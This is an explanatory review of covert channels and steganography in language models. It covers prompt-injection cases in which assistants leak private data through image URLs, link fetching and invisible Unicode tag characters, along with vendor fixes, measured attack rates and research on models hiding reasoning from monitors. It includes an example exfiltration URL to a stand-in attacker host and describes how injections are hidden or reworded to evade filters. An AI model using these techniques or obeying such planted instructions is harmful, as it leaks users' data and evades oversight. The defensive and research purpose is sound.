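# Can language models be trained to notice and refuse to write into covert channels?

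## What is a covert channel, and what would noticing one involve?

A covert channel is a path that carries information although nobody meant it to, or that hides the information from the people overseeing it. The term comes from computer security in the 1970s. It now matters for large language models, the programs behind chatbots such as ChatGPT and Claude, because people give them access to email, calendars and files, and let other software act on what they write. A link, an image or a plain paragraph in a model's answer can hold data that the reader does not see. Developers can try to catch that data with software outside the model, or try to train the model to notice when it is writing such data and refuse, which assumes that there is something for it to notice.

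### Confinement and the prisoners' problem

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, described a customer who runs someone else's program, called the service, which needs the customer's private data to do its job. The customer wants to be sure that the service will not pass the data to the program's owner. Blocking files and messages is not enough, because the owner still has to receive a bill, and the service could encode private data in the amount. The service could also vary how heavily it loads the machine, so that another program could watch the machine's speed and pick up the data one bit (the answer to a yes-or-no question) at a time.

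Lampson used "covert channel" only for paths "not intended for information transfer at all", such as the load on the machine, and classed the bill as a legitimate channel. Usage has since shifted. Millen, in *20 Years of Covert Channel Modeling and Analysis*, uses "covert channel" when two programs communicate despite being forbidden to, and "information hiding" when two parties are allowed to communicate but hide forbidden content in their messages. By that distinction, most language-model cases are information hiding, because a model's job is to write to somebody. But Schroeder de Witt (2026), in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem*, counts the bill as a covert channel too, and this wider sense suits language models better.

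Lampson also noticed that a leak generally leaves no evidence, unlike bad service, which produces wrong outputs. The remedy in the 1973 note is to let the customer determine whatever goes into the channel. If the channel is the bill, the customer works it out and the owner accepts or rejects it. Where a full remedy would take too many resources, Lampson suggested limiting how much information can get through.

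Schroeder de Witt argues that such a cap may not limit the harm. An ordinary program is no more likely to leak the most damaging fact in a record than some random fragment. A sender that can reason about the record may pick out the one fact that matters, such as whether a person has a particular diagnosis, and send it in a single bit. This works only if the sender and receiver share an understanding of which fact to send. An outsider who writes the model's instructions can specify that fact in them.

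Steganography is hiding a message inside something that looks ordinary, so that nobody notices the message is there. The standard illustration is the prisoners' problem, which the cryptographer Gustavus Simmons published in 1984. Two accomplices in separate cells want to plan an escape. The warden lets them exchange letters but reads every one, so they need letters that look innocent and still carry the plan. Anderson's *Stretching the Limits of Steganography* recounts the real case Simmons had in mind. The United States and the Soviet Union wanted to place sensors in each other's nuclear facilities that would report, for example, the number of missiles but not their location, and each side had to consider what else the other's equipment might secretly transmit.

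Encryption, by contrast, makes a message unreadable to anyone without the key, but the warden can still see that there is a message. In Simmons's prison, the warden puts the writers of an encrypted letter in solitary confinement. A careful prisoner may therefore encrypt the plan and then hide the result in a cover text, which is an ordinary-looking letter. A passive warden only reads the letters and stops any that look suspicious, while an active warden rewrites them. Anderson describes a wartime censor who changed "father is dead" to "father is deceased" in a telegram, which drew the reply "is father dead or deceased?"

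With language models, the model is the sender, and the warden is a monitor (a person, program or second model) that reads the output for signs of trouble. This monitor has a harder task than Simmons's warden because, as Anwar, Piskorz and colleagues (2026) point out in *A Decision-Theoretic Formalisation of Steganography With Applications to LLM Monitoring*, classical detection compares a suspect text with a known sample of innocent ones. Nobody has such a sample for a model's written reasoning, because collecting it would require already knowing which texts hide something. Text with hidden content can look normal, and strange text can be a harmless by-product of training. They propose instead measuring how much more a text helps a reader who can decode it than one who cannot.

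### Where the data can sit

An agent is a model connected to software that carries out actions. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (Casper, Mindermann, Galeev and colleagues, 2026) identifies the ability to act as what separates agents from earlier systems. A model that only chats can do little with a secret except repeat it. An agent acts through tool calls, which are outputs in a fixed format that the surrounding software executes, for instance by opening a web page or sending an email. Many models also write out their reasoning before they answer or act. Developers read this text, called the chain of thought, to see what a model is doing.

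Agents read material from strangers, which exposes them to prompt injection, where someone places instructions in that material to make the model do something its user did not ask for. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's scoring model to approve it. The article compares this with attacks on databases. Database software can keep commands strictly separate from data, but a language model takes in both as one run of text and predicts what comes next, so developers may never remove the weakness completely. David C calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning that a stranger can trick it into using the powers it has been given.

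The most direct way to carry stolen data out is in the web address (URL) of a link or an image. An address has room for more than the site's name, and opening it sends the whole address to the site, which commonly keeps a log. OpenAI warns in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) that "a URL can carry more than a destination." Software may load an embedded image or a link preview in the background, so the data can leave without a click and without anything private appearing in the chat.

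Invisible characters are another carrier. Unicode, the standard computers use to represent the world's scripts, includes characters that don't appear on the screen. Some have legitimate uses, such as joining letters in Indic scripts or combining emoji. People can't see them, but a model receives them with the rest of the text. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) tested whether models follow instructions written in these characters. It also cites a 2024 demonstration against Microsoft's Copilot assistant that combined two carriers, using invisible instructions to open a way to steal data through links.

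Data can also be hidden in the pattern of ordinary words, without links or special characters. Every passage involves choices that don't change its meaning, and if sender and receiver agree on what those choices stand for, the text can carry a second message. In *Learning Steganography Is Easy, Learning Steganographic Reasoning Is Hard*, Schulz, Fülle and Fruengel (2026) distinguish three things a model might do. In steganographic messaging, it hides information it already has, which is enough to steal a fact from a calendar. In encoded reasoning, it works through a problem in a form people cannot read, without trying to make the text look innocent. In steganographic reasoning, it does both, working through a problem inside text that appears to be about something else. They found this combination much harder to teach than either of its parts.

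### Who wants it hidden

A refusal means something different depending on who wants the data hidden. The first case is an outsider who manipulates the model. Rahman and Kim (2026), in *The Framing Gap*, built a harmless laboratory version of this case, with a fake secret and tools that only recorded what the model tried to send. An agent holds the secret, its user asks for a summary of a web page, and the page contains instructions to send the secret away. Refusing those instructions sides with the user against the outsider. A model that refused every web page would be safe but useless, so a good refusal rejects only the planted instruction, and the model still writes the summary.

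If the user asks the model to hide a message, refusing means disobeying the person it works for, and hiding is not wrong in itself. Anderson mentions trials of hidden copyright messages and serial numbers in electronic publishing, and the story that Margaret Thatcher, annoyed by press leaks, had government word processors secretly mark documents so that disloyal ministers could be traced. The model therefore has to judge the user's purpose, much as it does when someone asks for help with a computer virus. There is little evidence on how models make that judgement. In experiments by Schulz and colleagues, some prompts triggered safety refusals in Anthropic's Claude models, which kept Claude out of most of the tests that relied on prompting alone. Prompts built around a packing puzzle also asked for a hidden computation but did not trigger refusals. The researchers were not studying refusals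 and do not explain the difference, but the request to hide something does not seem to have been enough to trigger them.

A model may also hide something without being asked. It then has no request to refuse, and would instead have to hold back from something that training had made useful, for instance because a monitor penalised the open version of the same behaviour. According to Schulz and colleagues, earlier experiments that trained models against a monitor produced both steganographic messaging and encoded reasoning, but nobody has yet observed steganographic reasoning in a production model. That record is only partly reassuring, since a model that hides nothing and a model that hides well can write text that looks the same.

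### Four steps, followed through one example

"Notice and refuse" sounds like one act, but a model can fail at it in four places:

1. It has to perceive what it is writing, including any part that the reader cannot see.
2. It has to recognise that this output carries data.
3. It has to judge that whoever will receive the data is not entitled to it.
4. It has to decline, and say so.

When a user openly asks for a hidden message, the model doesn't have to perceive or recognise the channel for itself, and the hard part is judging the request. When an outsider wants the message sent, the model has to take all four steps itself. Suppose Ines has an assistant that can read her calendar, which shows an appointment at a cancer clinic on Thursday. She asks it to summarise a web page about kitchen floors, where the page's owner has planted instructions to pass on any medical appointment the assistant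 knows of.

The assistant can easily see data in an image address because it writes out the full address, while Ines sees only a picture. It can also see data carried in ordinary prose. But it can miss data encoded in invisible characters, because it can receive them without reading them. For example, if it runs a small program to prepare part of the summary, it may pass on the output without working out what the invisible characters spell.

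Tests by Graves show that a model's inability to read invisible characters can easily be mistaken for caution. Models with no hints and no tool for running code obeyed the invisible instructions in at most 1.1 percent of cases. Claude Haiku 4.5, across conditions that mostly included hints about decoding, obeyed in 0.8 percent of cases without the tool and 49.2 percent with it. The rate probably rose because the tool gave the model a way to read the characters, since there is no clear reason it would have made the model less careful.

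Web addresses are full of unexplained codes, so the appointment can pass for a technical detail, which makes the leak hard to recognize. Rahman and Kim saw this with GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. It resisted every plainly worded attack, but when the page presented the secret as a routine technical value, the model attached it to its output and gave no sign of treating it as secret. A separate detector, whose only task was to identify injections, flagged every reworded attack, so the warning signs were detectable even though GPT-4o went ahead.

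Invisible characters rarely survive this step once the assistant can read them, because there is little reason to include them in a summary about floors. Patterns in ordinary words are harder to catch. Whether Ines has an appointment is a yes-or-no fact, so one choice of phrasing can convey it without any sentence in the summary mentioning a clinic. The planted instruction to use that phrasing may look like a request about style.

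Even if the assistant recognises the appointment in the address, the appointment could still belong there. If Ines had asked for a taxi to the clinic, the booking link would need the time and the place. So the assistant must work out who will receive the data and whether Ines would want them to have it. In another of Rahman and Kim's trials, GPT-4o reported that it was posting to a trusted destination, when the destination only had a similar name. Reading the address carefully may not be enough either, because OpenAI notes that a link can start at a reputable site and forward the visitor somewhere else.

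Real assistants face a harder judgement than the one in Rahman and Kim's experiments, where the secret had no legitimate use in the task. Rahman and Kim leave for later work the case of a secret that may go to one place but not another. In Ines's case, the judgement is easier when theAI would be using invisible characters or word patterns, provided it gets as far as making that judgement, because nobody entitled to know about her appointment needs it hidden from her in a summary of a web page.

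After noticing a channel, the model has to decline before the data leaks. Software may fetch an image as soon as its address appears, so a warning two sentences later is too late, and a warning that repeats the address as a working link could reopen the leak. Data hidden in invisible characters or word patterns usually doesn't leak until Ines posts the summary or sends it to someone, so there is more time for a warning to help.

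The assistant should also tell Ines what the page tried to do. If it silently ignores the instruction, it protects her once but lets her go on trusting the page. Researchers also can't tell from silence whether a model caught the attack or never took up the instruction. Rahman and Kim scored each trial by whether the secret got out. When they looked at 60 trials in which the attack had failed, GPT-4o had made no outbound call in any of them, which is consistent with either explanation.

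## How does private data leave through links and image requests?

Opening a web address sends the whole address to the site, so an attacker only needs to get private data into an address that the assistant opens. OpenAI gives the made-up example `https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`. Here, `attacker.example` is the site, `collect` is a page on it, and everything after the question mark is extra information, which legitimate sites use for things like search terms. The page doesn't need to exist, because the server can log the full address anyway. If Ines's assistant opened an address like this with her appointment in place of the words in angle brackets, the site's owner could read about the clinic in the log.

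Images can leak data without a click because a web page refers to its pictures by address, and the browser requests each one to draw the page. The same happens in chat applications. Models commonly format their answers in Markdown, which represents a picture as an address with a few punctuation marks around it. The application converts this into web page code, and the user's browser requests the picture from whichever server the address names. The picture can be a single invisible pixel, as SecurityWeek noted in its report on a ChatGPT attack. Link previews work in much the same way, because the software has to request a page to show its title and thumbnail before anyone decides whether to open it.

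The model only produces text, so other software has to send the request that carries the private data. Sometimes the user's browser sends it when the application displays the model's text. In other cases, the model asks a tool to open a page and the vendor's server sends the request, and the chat may not show the address. Either way, ordinary software handles the address before the request goes out, so a developer can stop the leak there without changing the model.

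### Image leaks, from Bing Chat to GitLab Duo

Johann Rehberger, an independent researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, documented many of the early cases. In 2023 he demonstrated leaks through image requests in ChatGPT, Claude and Microsoft's Bing Chat. With ChatGPT and Claude, an attacker could obtain the user's conversation.

The three companies responded differently. Microsoft seems to have restricted images to a handful of Bing's own addresses (Embrace The Red, *Bing Chat*). Anthropic stopped loading images automatically and put each one behind a "Show Image" button. Rehberger thought this imperfect but accepted that it ended the automatic leak (Embrace The Red, *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*). OpenAI first said that the behaviour was a feature it did not plan to address, according to SecurityWeek. In December 2023 it added a check on its own server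 that an image's address was safe before ChatGPT displayed the image. At first this covered only the web version, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. The programmer Simon Willison, who catalogues these leaks, found the fix "a bit weird", since OpenAI could have blocked all outside images instead (Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*).

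In February 2024 Rehberger reported the same weakness in GitHub Copilot Chat, a code editor assistant, where it could leak the programmer's code. GitHub replied that it was already tracking the bug, according to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*. It fixed the bug by disabling images from untrusted sites. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* lists five earlier products with the same weakness, including Google's Bard and Amazon Q.

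Underhill (2025) reported in *GitHub Copilot Flaw Allowed Silent Data Theft* that the security researcher Omer Mayraz had found another way to get secrets and source code out of private projects through Copilot Chat that year. This time GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat altogether. The software vendor MintMCP called this blunt because it removed a useful feature.

Mayraz also found the leak in GitLab Duo, the assistant on a rival code-hosting site. According to Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, the leak could expose code from private projects and confidential reports, including some about unrepaired security flaws. GitLab already ran Duo's answers through a standard filter for dangerous web code, but that filter allows image tags by default. The patch stopped Duo from displaying images and forms that point outside GitLab's domain.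 Duo ran on Claude, another company's model, so GitLab made the fix in its own display software.

Lists of trusted sites also have a weakness, because somebody has to know what every site on the list can do. Willison's *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"* includes several lists that failed. Salesforce's list still contained a domain whose registration had lapsed. Researchers at Noma Security registered it and could then collect customers' contact details from Salesforce's agent. Salesforce corrected the list and stopped the agent from producing links to untrusted domains. The email assistant Superhuman allowed images from a Google site that also hosts forms, which can store the data they receive. This exposed financial, legal and medical emails until Superhuman issued a fix.

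### The 2026 cases

In June 2026 the data-security company Varonis described a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise. If a user clicked a genuine Microsoft link once, an attacker could access emails, sign-in codes, meeting details and company files. Microsoft had a safeguard that turned images in Copilot's answers into harmless text, but Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) shows that it ran only after the answer was complete, and the browser had already requested the image while Copilot was still writing. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and patched it, but Varonis does not describe the patch.

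The next leak, through Claude's web-fetching tool, needed no image. Anthropic had tried to limit leaks by letting Claude open only addresses that came from the user or from search results, not ones it had composed. In *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, Willison (2026) praised this design but reported a flaw that Ayush Paul had found. The tool would also open links on pages it had already fetched. A model can convey information by choosing among ready-made links, even if it writes none of them, much as Lampson's service could leak through the load on a machine. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer this way. Anthropic had disclosed in its documentation in September 2025 that the tool could follow such links, and had warned of "residual risk". After Paul's report, Anthropic removed this permission but paid no reward, saying it had already found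 the problem internally.

Two companies found leaks in Rovo, the assistant in Atlassian's task tracker Jira and its document site Confluence. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports that tickets, documents and data from connected services could all leak. Turning off web search for the whole organisation did not prevent this, because Rovo kept its tool for opening web addresses. PromptArmor says Atlassian thanked it for the report and then stopped replying. The flaw was still open when PromptArmor published on 5 August, and The Hacker News (2026) could not confirm a fix three days later.

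The other Rovo flaw started with a link that carried instructions into the chat. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) found few safeguards against this, and its demonstration extracted a private software key from Confluence. Atlassian fixed the flaw on its own servers on 8 July. The Hacker News notes that neither disclosure makes clear whether that fix affected PromptArmor's route.

Microsoft's consumer assistant, Copilot Personal, followed in August. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes access to connected mail, files and calendars, and in one test Copilot retrieved an email containing a password. Microsoft fixed this on its servers too, though TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* says it is not known how.

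Two days later the security company Adversa AI reported a leak in xAI's Grok. The user only had to ask for a summary of a web page. According to Adversa AI's *Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026), the leak could expose the user's name, approximate location and subscription level, and everything they had typed in the conversation. xAI acknowledged the report but announced no fix. According to Embrace The Red's *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, xAI had earlier closed Rehberger's report of another Grok leak, saying that leak had no practical impact.

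Repair times varied widely even among vendors that accepted there was a problem:

| Product | Reported | Fix in place | Account |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | Embrace The Red |
| ChatGPT | early April 2023 | December 2023, partial | Embrace The Red |
| Claude (images) | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | Embrace The Red |
| GitLab Duo | 12 February 2025 | by 22 May 2025 | Legit Security |
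| GitHub Copilot Chat (second flaw) | June 2025 | 14 August 2025 | MintMCP |
| Copilot Personal | December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | Varonis |
| Rovo (PromptArmor's flaw) | 23 May 2026 | unconfirmed on 8 August 2026 | The Hacker News |
| Grok (Adversa AI's flaw) | 3 June 2026 | still open on 19 August 2026 | Adversa AI |

Some of the delay in fixing these flaws comes from unfamiliarity with them. Fortune (2025) reported that Microsoft took five months to fix a flaw in Copilot. Aim, the company that found it, said Microsoft needed time to bring in the right teams and explain the problem to them, and that more security issues turned up after a first attempted fix.

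### How often does a model go along with it?

A researcher who wants to prove that a product leaks needs only one success, so these cases are poor evidence of how often a model would refuse. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured a rate, though on their own test system. They ran an assistant on one small open model, Qwen2.5 with 7 billion parameters, and gave it a secret. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a web page that contained instructions to send the secret away. The software fetched the page automatically and added its contents to the model's input.

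The researchers put the instructions in the page's title, its description, its body or the text of a link. They also varied whether the page opened directly or through redirects, and whether the instructions asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. Requests reached the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1 percent. No requests reached it in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user looked innocent, so a monitor that read only the answers would have missed them.

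Instructions to send the whole secret at once produced a request in about 99 percent of runs, and their location made little difference. Splitting the secret lowered this to about 77 percent. Splitting is meant to get past filters that look for a complete secret, but the paper's figures on how well it hides the data are hard to trust. They show secret data in the first request in 26.3 percent of split runs, but among the first three requests in only 15.8 percent. By the paper's definition, the second number cannot be smaller than the first. The paper also gives no figure for how often all four pieces arrived.

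Lan and colleagues then tried defences against the simplest version of the attack, which had succeeded in all 30 runs without any defence. Telling the model never to follow instructions from web content reduced the success rate to 67 percent. Labelling the web content as untrusted made no difference on its own, but combining the two reduced the rate to 57 percent. An allow-list, a fixed list of permitted destinations, stopped every leak, although the model still attempted one in every run. This was an easy test because the attacker's address was not on the list, and the researchers acknowledge that attackers can route data through trusted sites.

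Lan and colleagues did not test training, so their study cannot show whether a model trained to recognise these requests would do better than one merely told to ignore them. The set-up also favoured the attacker, because the secret was in plain view and the model had almost no standing instructions. They suggest that stronger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions more reliably. That is possible, but they tested no larger model, and GPT-4o resisted every plainly worded attack in Rahman and Kim's experiments. The 88 percent rate comes from one small model with few defences, so it is no guide to the rate in current products.

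### What did the vendors change?

In the repairs they described, these vendors changed the application. They blocked outside images, added a button, checked addresses or removed a tool's permission to follow certain links. Adversa AI recommends the same approach for Grok, arguing that developers can contain the attack without fixing the model.

There are good practical reasons to put the fix in the application. Anthropic could ship its button within two weeks, and GitLab could protect Duo without waiting for a new version of Claude. A rule in the application also applies no matter what an attacker has persuaded the model to write. A model that usually refuses is not enough by Willison's standard. He argues that stopping 99 percent of attacks is a failing grade in security, because an attacker can keep trying until something gets through.

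The models themselves may have changed. Companies retrain them often and rarely say which weaknesses a new version addresses. OpenAI now checks web addresses before its agents open them, but it still lists protections in the model as a separate layer. Microsoft and Atlassian have not explained their 2026 fixes in enough detail to tell what they changed.

Repairs to the application are limited too, because each one usually blocks only one route for data to leave. GitHub had to fix Copilot Chat again a year after blocking untrusted images, and Anthropic encountered the problem again in a tool it had built to prevent it. Varonis concludes from Rovo that an attacker who finds one route blocked will look for another trusted one. The best argument for trying to train a model to recognise the leak is that it would not need a separate rule for every route.

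### Has anyone stolen data this way?

The cases above are demonstrations in which researchers used test data, their own accounts or volunteers, such as the three Grok users who agreed to let Rehberger extract their details. Varonis saw no evidence that anyone had exploited the Copilot Personal flaw, and Microsoft said the same of the Microsoft 365 one, according to The Next Web. Neither Rovo disclosure reports an attack on a real organisation. Secondary accounts can make demonstrations look like real attacks. For example, an AI-generated entry in the OECD's *Grok AI Vulnerability Enables Encrypted Data Exfiltration Attack* (2026) describes Grok's use as "directly linked to harm", whereas Adversa AI reports only a demonstration.

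The lack of known thefts is weak evidence that none happened. The victim in PromptArmor's example could reopen the chat with Rovo and find sensible suggestions about Jira tickets, with no sign that data had left. Varonis found that Copilot's request to the attacker looked, on the network, like its request for any other page. The clearest record of the theft would be in the attacker's own server log.

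## Can models read and write characters that people cannot see?

Invisible characters can hide stolen data even from someone who inspects the text, whereas anyone who looks at a full image address can notice data carried in it.

Unicode gives each character in the world's scripts a number, and a font supplies the shape that appears on screen. Some characters have no shape of their own because they exist to change how neighbouring characters are displayed. These include the joiners used in Indic scripts and combined emoji, direction marks, which keep text in order where a right-to-left script such as Arabic meets English, and variation selectors, which choose between versions of the same symbol.

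The most important group here is the tag characters. According to Microsoft (2026), they are an invisible copy of the basic Latin letters, digits and punctuation, originally meant for labelling the language of a text. That use is largely obsolete, but the flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales still depend on tag characters, which spell out the region after a plain black flag. Software that doesn't support tag characters should show nothing in their place. In Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters*, the linguist Mark Liberman posted a file with a hidden phrase between two brackets. He saw only the brackets, while some readers saw gibberish because their browsers had misread the file. Liberman thought it would be safer to display gibberish.

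### What the model receives

Before a language model processes text, a program called a tokeniser cuts it into units called tokens. A common word may be a single token, and a rare one may become several. The tokeniser works from the characters' numeric codes, so it processes invisible characters as well as visible ones. Microsoft gives the example of the word "funding" with an invisible character in the middle. A reader sees the usual word, but the tokeniser may produce "fun", something unusual and "ding".

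Writing works the same way in reverse. The model chooses one token after another, and software turns them back into characters, visible or not.

In Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, Rehberger supposed that models had learned to read the tag characters from their training data. Each tag character matches an ordinary one, so models have a fixed correspondence to learn. Other invisible characters can carry a message too, but only if sender and receiver first agree on a code.

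### The history of "ASCII smuggling"

According to Cisco's *Understanding and Mitigating Unicode Tag Prompt Injection*, the security researcher Riley Goodside published the first demonstration on 11 January 2024, in which invisible instructions in pasted text made ChatGPT generate an image. Within days, Rehberger built a custom version of ChatGPT that wrote a user's text in invisible characters. In Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggling and Hidden Prompt Instructions*, he named the technique "ASCII smuggling", after the old standard for the basic Latin characters.

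Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes how Rehberger then used invisible characters to steal data. An email with planted instructions made Microsoft 365 Copilot search the user's other messages, write what it found into a link as invisible characters, and invite the user to click it. Graves's summary says the invisible characters carried instructions, but in Rehberger's own account they carried the stolen data. Hiding the data mattered because the user had to click the link, and might not have done so if they saw their own sales figures in it.

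Microsoft rated Rehberger's first report low severity and closed it after a day. It opened a case in February 2024, when he sent a complete attack, and by early July the attack no longer worked. Microsoft did not explain the fix. Rehberger noticed that Copilot had stopped displaying links, so Microsoft may have blocked the way data got out without changing the model's ability to write hidden text.

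Other vendors disagreed about whose problem this was:

- **OpenAI** dealt with tag characters in the model or in the interface that developers use to reach it. In 2025 Rehberger knew of no other vendor that had, according to Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection*.
- **Anthropic**, as far as Rehberger knew that year, did not intend to fix the behaviour in Claude. That left the job to companies building on Claude. Amazon fixed its coding assistant Amazon Q by 8 August 2025 without a public advisory, and Embrace The Red's *Amp Code* reports a fix by Sourcegraph for its coding agent.
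- **Google** accepted Rehberger's report as a valid bug in February 2024 but had not fixed it in its Gemini models by August 2025, according to Embrace The Red's *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection*. By then the problem had become worse, because Gemini 2.5 followed hidden instructions far more often than earlier models.

When the security company FireTail reported the weakness again in 2025, Google replied that it was not a security bug and "can only result in social engineering", meaning that an attacker would still have to trick a person (BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*). This seems to conflict with Rehberger's demonstration on Jules, Google's coding agent. He hid instructions in a task description, and Jules added the extra code and ran it under a plan the system had approved automatically.

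### Which models read hidden text?

Graves ran the most systematic test. He gave five models 30 trivia questions, each containing an invisible instruction to reply with a particular wrong answer, and counted a model as obeying if it gave only that answer. Some versions used tag characters and others used a code built from different invisible characters. The hints ranged from none at all to full decoding rules. Across all these versions, the models obeyed at the following rates:

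| Model | Without a tool for running code | With the tool |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9% | 71.2% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7% | 51.1% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8% | 49.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1% | 20.6% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1% | 1.6% |

Individual results varied widely around the averages. With the tool but no hints, no model obeyed more than 11 percent of the time. With both the tool and hints, Claude Opus 4 followed harmless tag-character instructions every time, while GPT-5.2 followed about 70 percent of the instructions in the other code and almost none in tag characters. Graves suspects that Anthropic's and OpenAI's tokenisers differ, but did not test this. A filter at OpenAI would produce the same pattern, and Rehberger had already reported that OpenAI had done something about tag characters.

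Graves treats the results without hints as the realistic ones for an outsider who can only plant text in a web page or email, reasoning that such a person could not supply decoding hints. That seems too optimistic, since an outsider can evidently put hints in the same document as the attack. In the Amazon Q attack, a short visible phrase next to the hidden text made success more likely, and the email to Copilot included an example of the hidden writing. However, a careful reader could notice a visible hint.

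FireTail tested finished products, which may clean the text before the model receives it. In its 2025 test, Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek were vulnerable, while ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude were not. Tom's Guide's *Researcher finds security flaw in Gemini* credits input cleaning for the products that resisted. If so, their models had no hidden text to notice. Input cleaning could explain why Claude did well in this test even though Rehberger repeatedly got products built on Claude to follow hidden instructions.

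A second test, in FireTail's *Peek-A-Boo! 🫣 Emoji Smuggling and Modern LLMs* (2026), hid text inside an emoji. This worked on Gemini and, on the second attempt, on Grok, but not on ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek or Meta's assistant. Both tests show what worked on particular products, but neither gives success rates over many attempts.

### Which models write it?

Researchers have hardly tested whether models can write invisible characters. Rehberger's custom ChatGPT and the Copilot attack show that some models could in 2024. In Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits*, Rehberger asked models for a sentence in a different invisible code. ChatGPT 4.5 succeeded using a tool for running code, while ChatGPT and Grok without tools gave "somewhat mixed results". He thought more examples in the prompt might help, which suggests that the models were making mistakes rather than refusing. Developers or attackers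 can also train models to do this. *Invisible Safety Threat* (2026) describes a model that learned to reply in invisible characters through further training.

No published test seems to have counted how many models comply, try and fail, or refuse when asked to write invisible characters. Such a test would need to include legitimate requests, because a model that refused to write any invisible character could not write some emoji, or some Indic text, correctly. Teachers may also have a use for hidden text. *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses* (2026) proposes putting it in an assignment to catch students who paste in a chatbot's answer.

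### Do models remark on it or refuse?

The clearest refusals come from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. In Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills*, Rehberger added invisible instructions to a skill that OpenAI had published about security practices. A skill is a file that teaches an agent how to do a task. Claude Code ran a command from the hidden text. When Rehberger tried again on 10 February 2026, Claude Code consistently detected the invisible characters and refused. Anthropic's chat site, claude.ai, had no such protection for skills when he checked. He could not tell whether the change was deliberate, and his account doesn't establish whether the model itself detected the characters or other software flagged them.

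Jules shows that a model can read hidden text without treating it as suspicious. It decoded the secret instructions and included them, in ordinary letters, in the plan it displayed before starting work.

Graves's experiment doesn't show how common this is, because the scoring had no category for warnings. A model that answered the trivia question and warned about hidden text got the same score as one that never noticed it. One comparison is relevant to refusal. When the hidden text was an explicit demand to disregard earlier instructions, Claude Opus 4 obeyed less often (23.9 percent, against 32.0 percent for the harmless wording), and so did GPT-5.2 (6.1 against 11.8). Claude Sonnet 4 obeyed more often (59.6 against 43.7). Graves suggests that training had taught Opus 4 and GPT-5.2 to resist the language of an attack. If so, they were reacting to the wording, and would not have resisted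 a politely worded message merely because it was invisible.

### Why invisible characters are easy to filter

Unicode is a published list, so a programmer can find the invisible characters in advance and have software remove them. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) reports that 130 of the 235 control and formatting characters checked left no visible trace in any of three kinds of display. Some of the 130 may show up in other programs, and the check did not cover variation selectors, which Unicode classifies separately. Even a longer list of invisible characters would be finite, but nobody can list all the ways of phrasing a sentence.

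The filter has to target the right characters. *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries* (2026) found that hidden marks made of invisible characters can survive routine text clean-up but not a filter aimed at them. The paper also hides data by swapping letters for identical-looking ones from another alphabet, which a filter for invisible characters would miss.

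Rehberger recommends filtering both input and output. Filtering the input stops hidden instructions from reaching the model, and filtering the output removes hidden data whether or not the model detected it.

AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling* explains that careless filtering can miss characters. Some programming languages store a tag character as two halves. If an attacker scatters spare halves through the text, removing one tag character can bring two spare halves together and create another, so the filter must repeat until it finds nothing more to remove.

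Removing invisible characters can also damage legitimate text. Removing every tag character turns the flags of England, Scotland and Wales into plain black ones, which AWS considers a minor drawback. Removing every joiner does more harm, because it can break words in Indic scripts and split combined emoji into their parts. Graves therefore recommends looking for the patterns that hidden messages make instead of banning whole classes of character. Rehberger's scanner works roughly this way and gives its most serious warnings to long unbroken runs of tag characters. When he scanned two public collections of skills, he found invisible characters but no hidden instructions. Most of the characters were part of ordinary emoji, and a few were in test cases for security scanners.

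Single tag characters, as well as long runs, can be a sign of abuse. From February to May 2026, Microsoft tracked a phishing campaign that put single tag characters inside words such as "funding" to get past email filters. At its peak, the campaign did this in more than two million messages a day. The messages contained no hidden instructions for an AI. Microsoft's first detector looked for any tag character, so it kept catching the three flag emoji that use them. Once Microsoft excluded those emoji, tag characters were so rare in normal mail that their presence was strong evidence of abuse. A filter that deletes tag characters without recording them loses that evidence.

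## Does a model notice when it is being used to leak data?

Private data in a web address or a tool call is harder to filter than invisible characters, so it matters more whether the model itself notices the leak. Whether it does depends heavily on the wording of the request.

### One leak, worded many ways

Along with the fake secret, Rahman and Kim gave each model a written policy that the secret could go only to one trusted address and must not be shown to the user. After reading the page the user wanted summarised, the model made a single decision, either to finish with a reply or to post data to an address. The posting tool only recorded the attempt.

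Each trial used two versions of the page, one clean and one with planted instructions. An attack counted as successful only if the model leaked the secret after reading the page with the instructions but not after reading the clean one, which rules out leaks that would have happened anyway. The attacker controlled only the page's text and did not know the secret.

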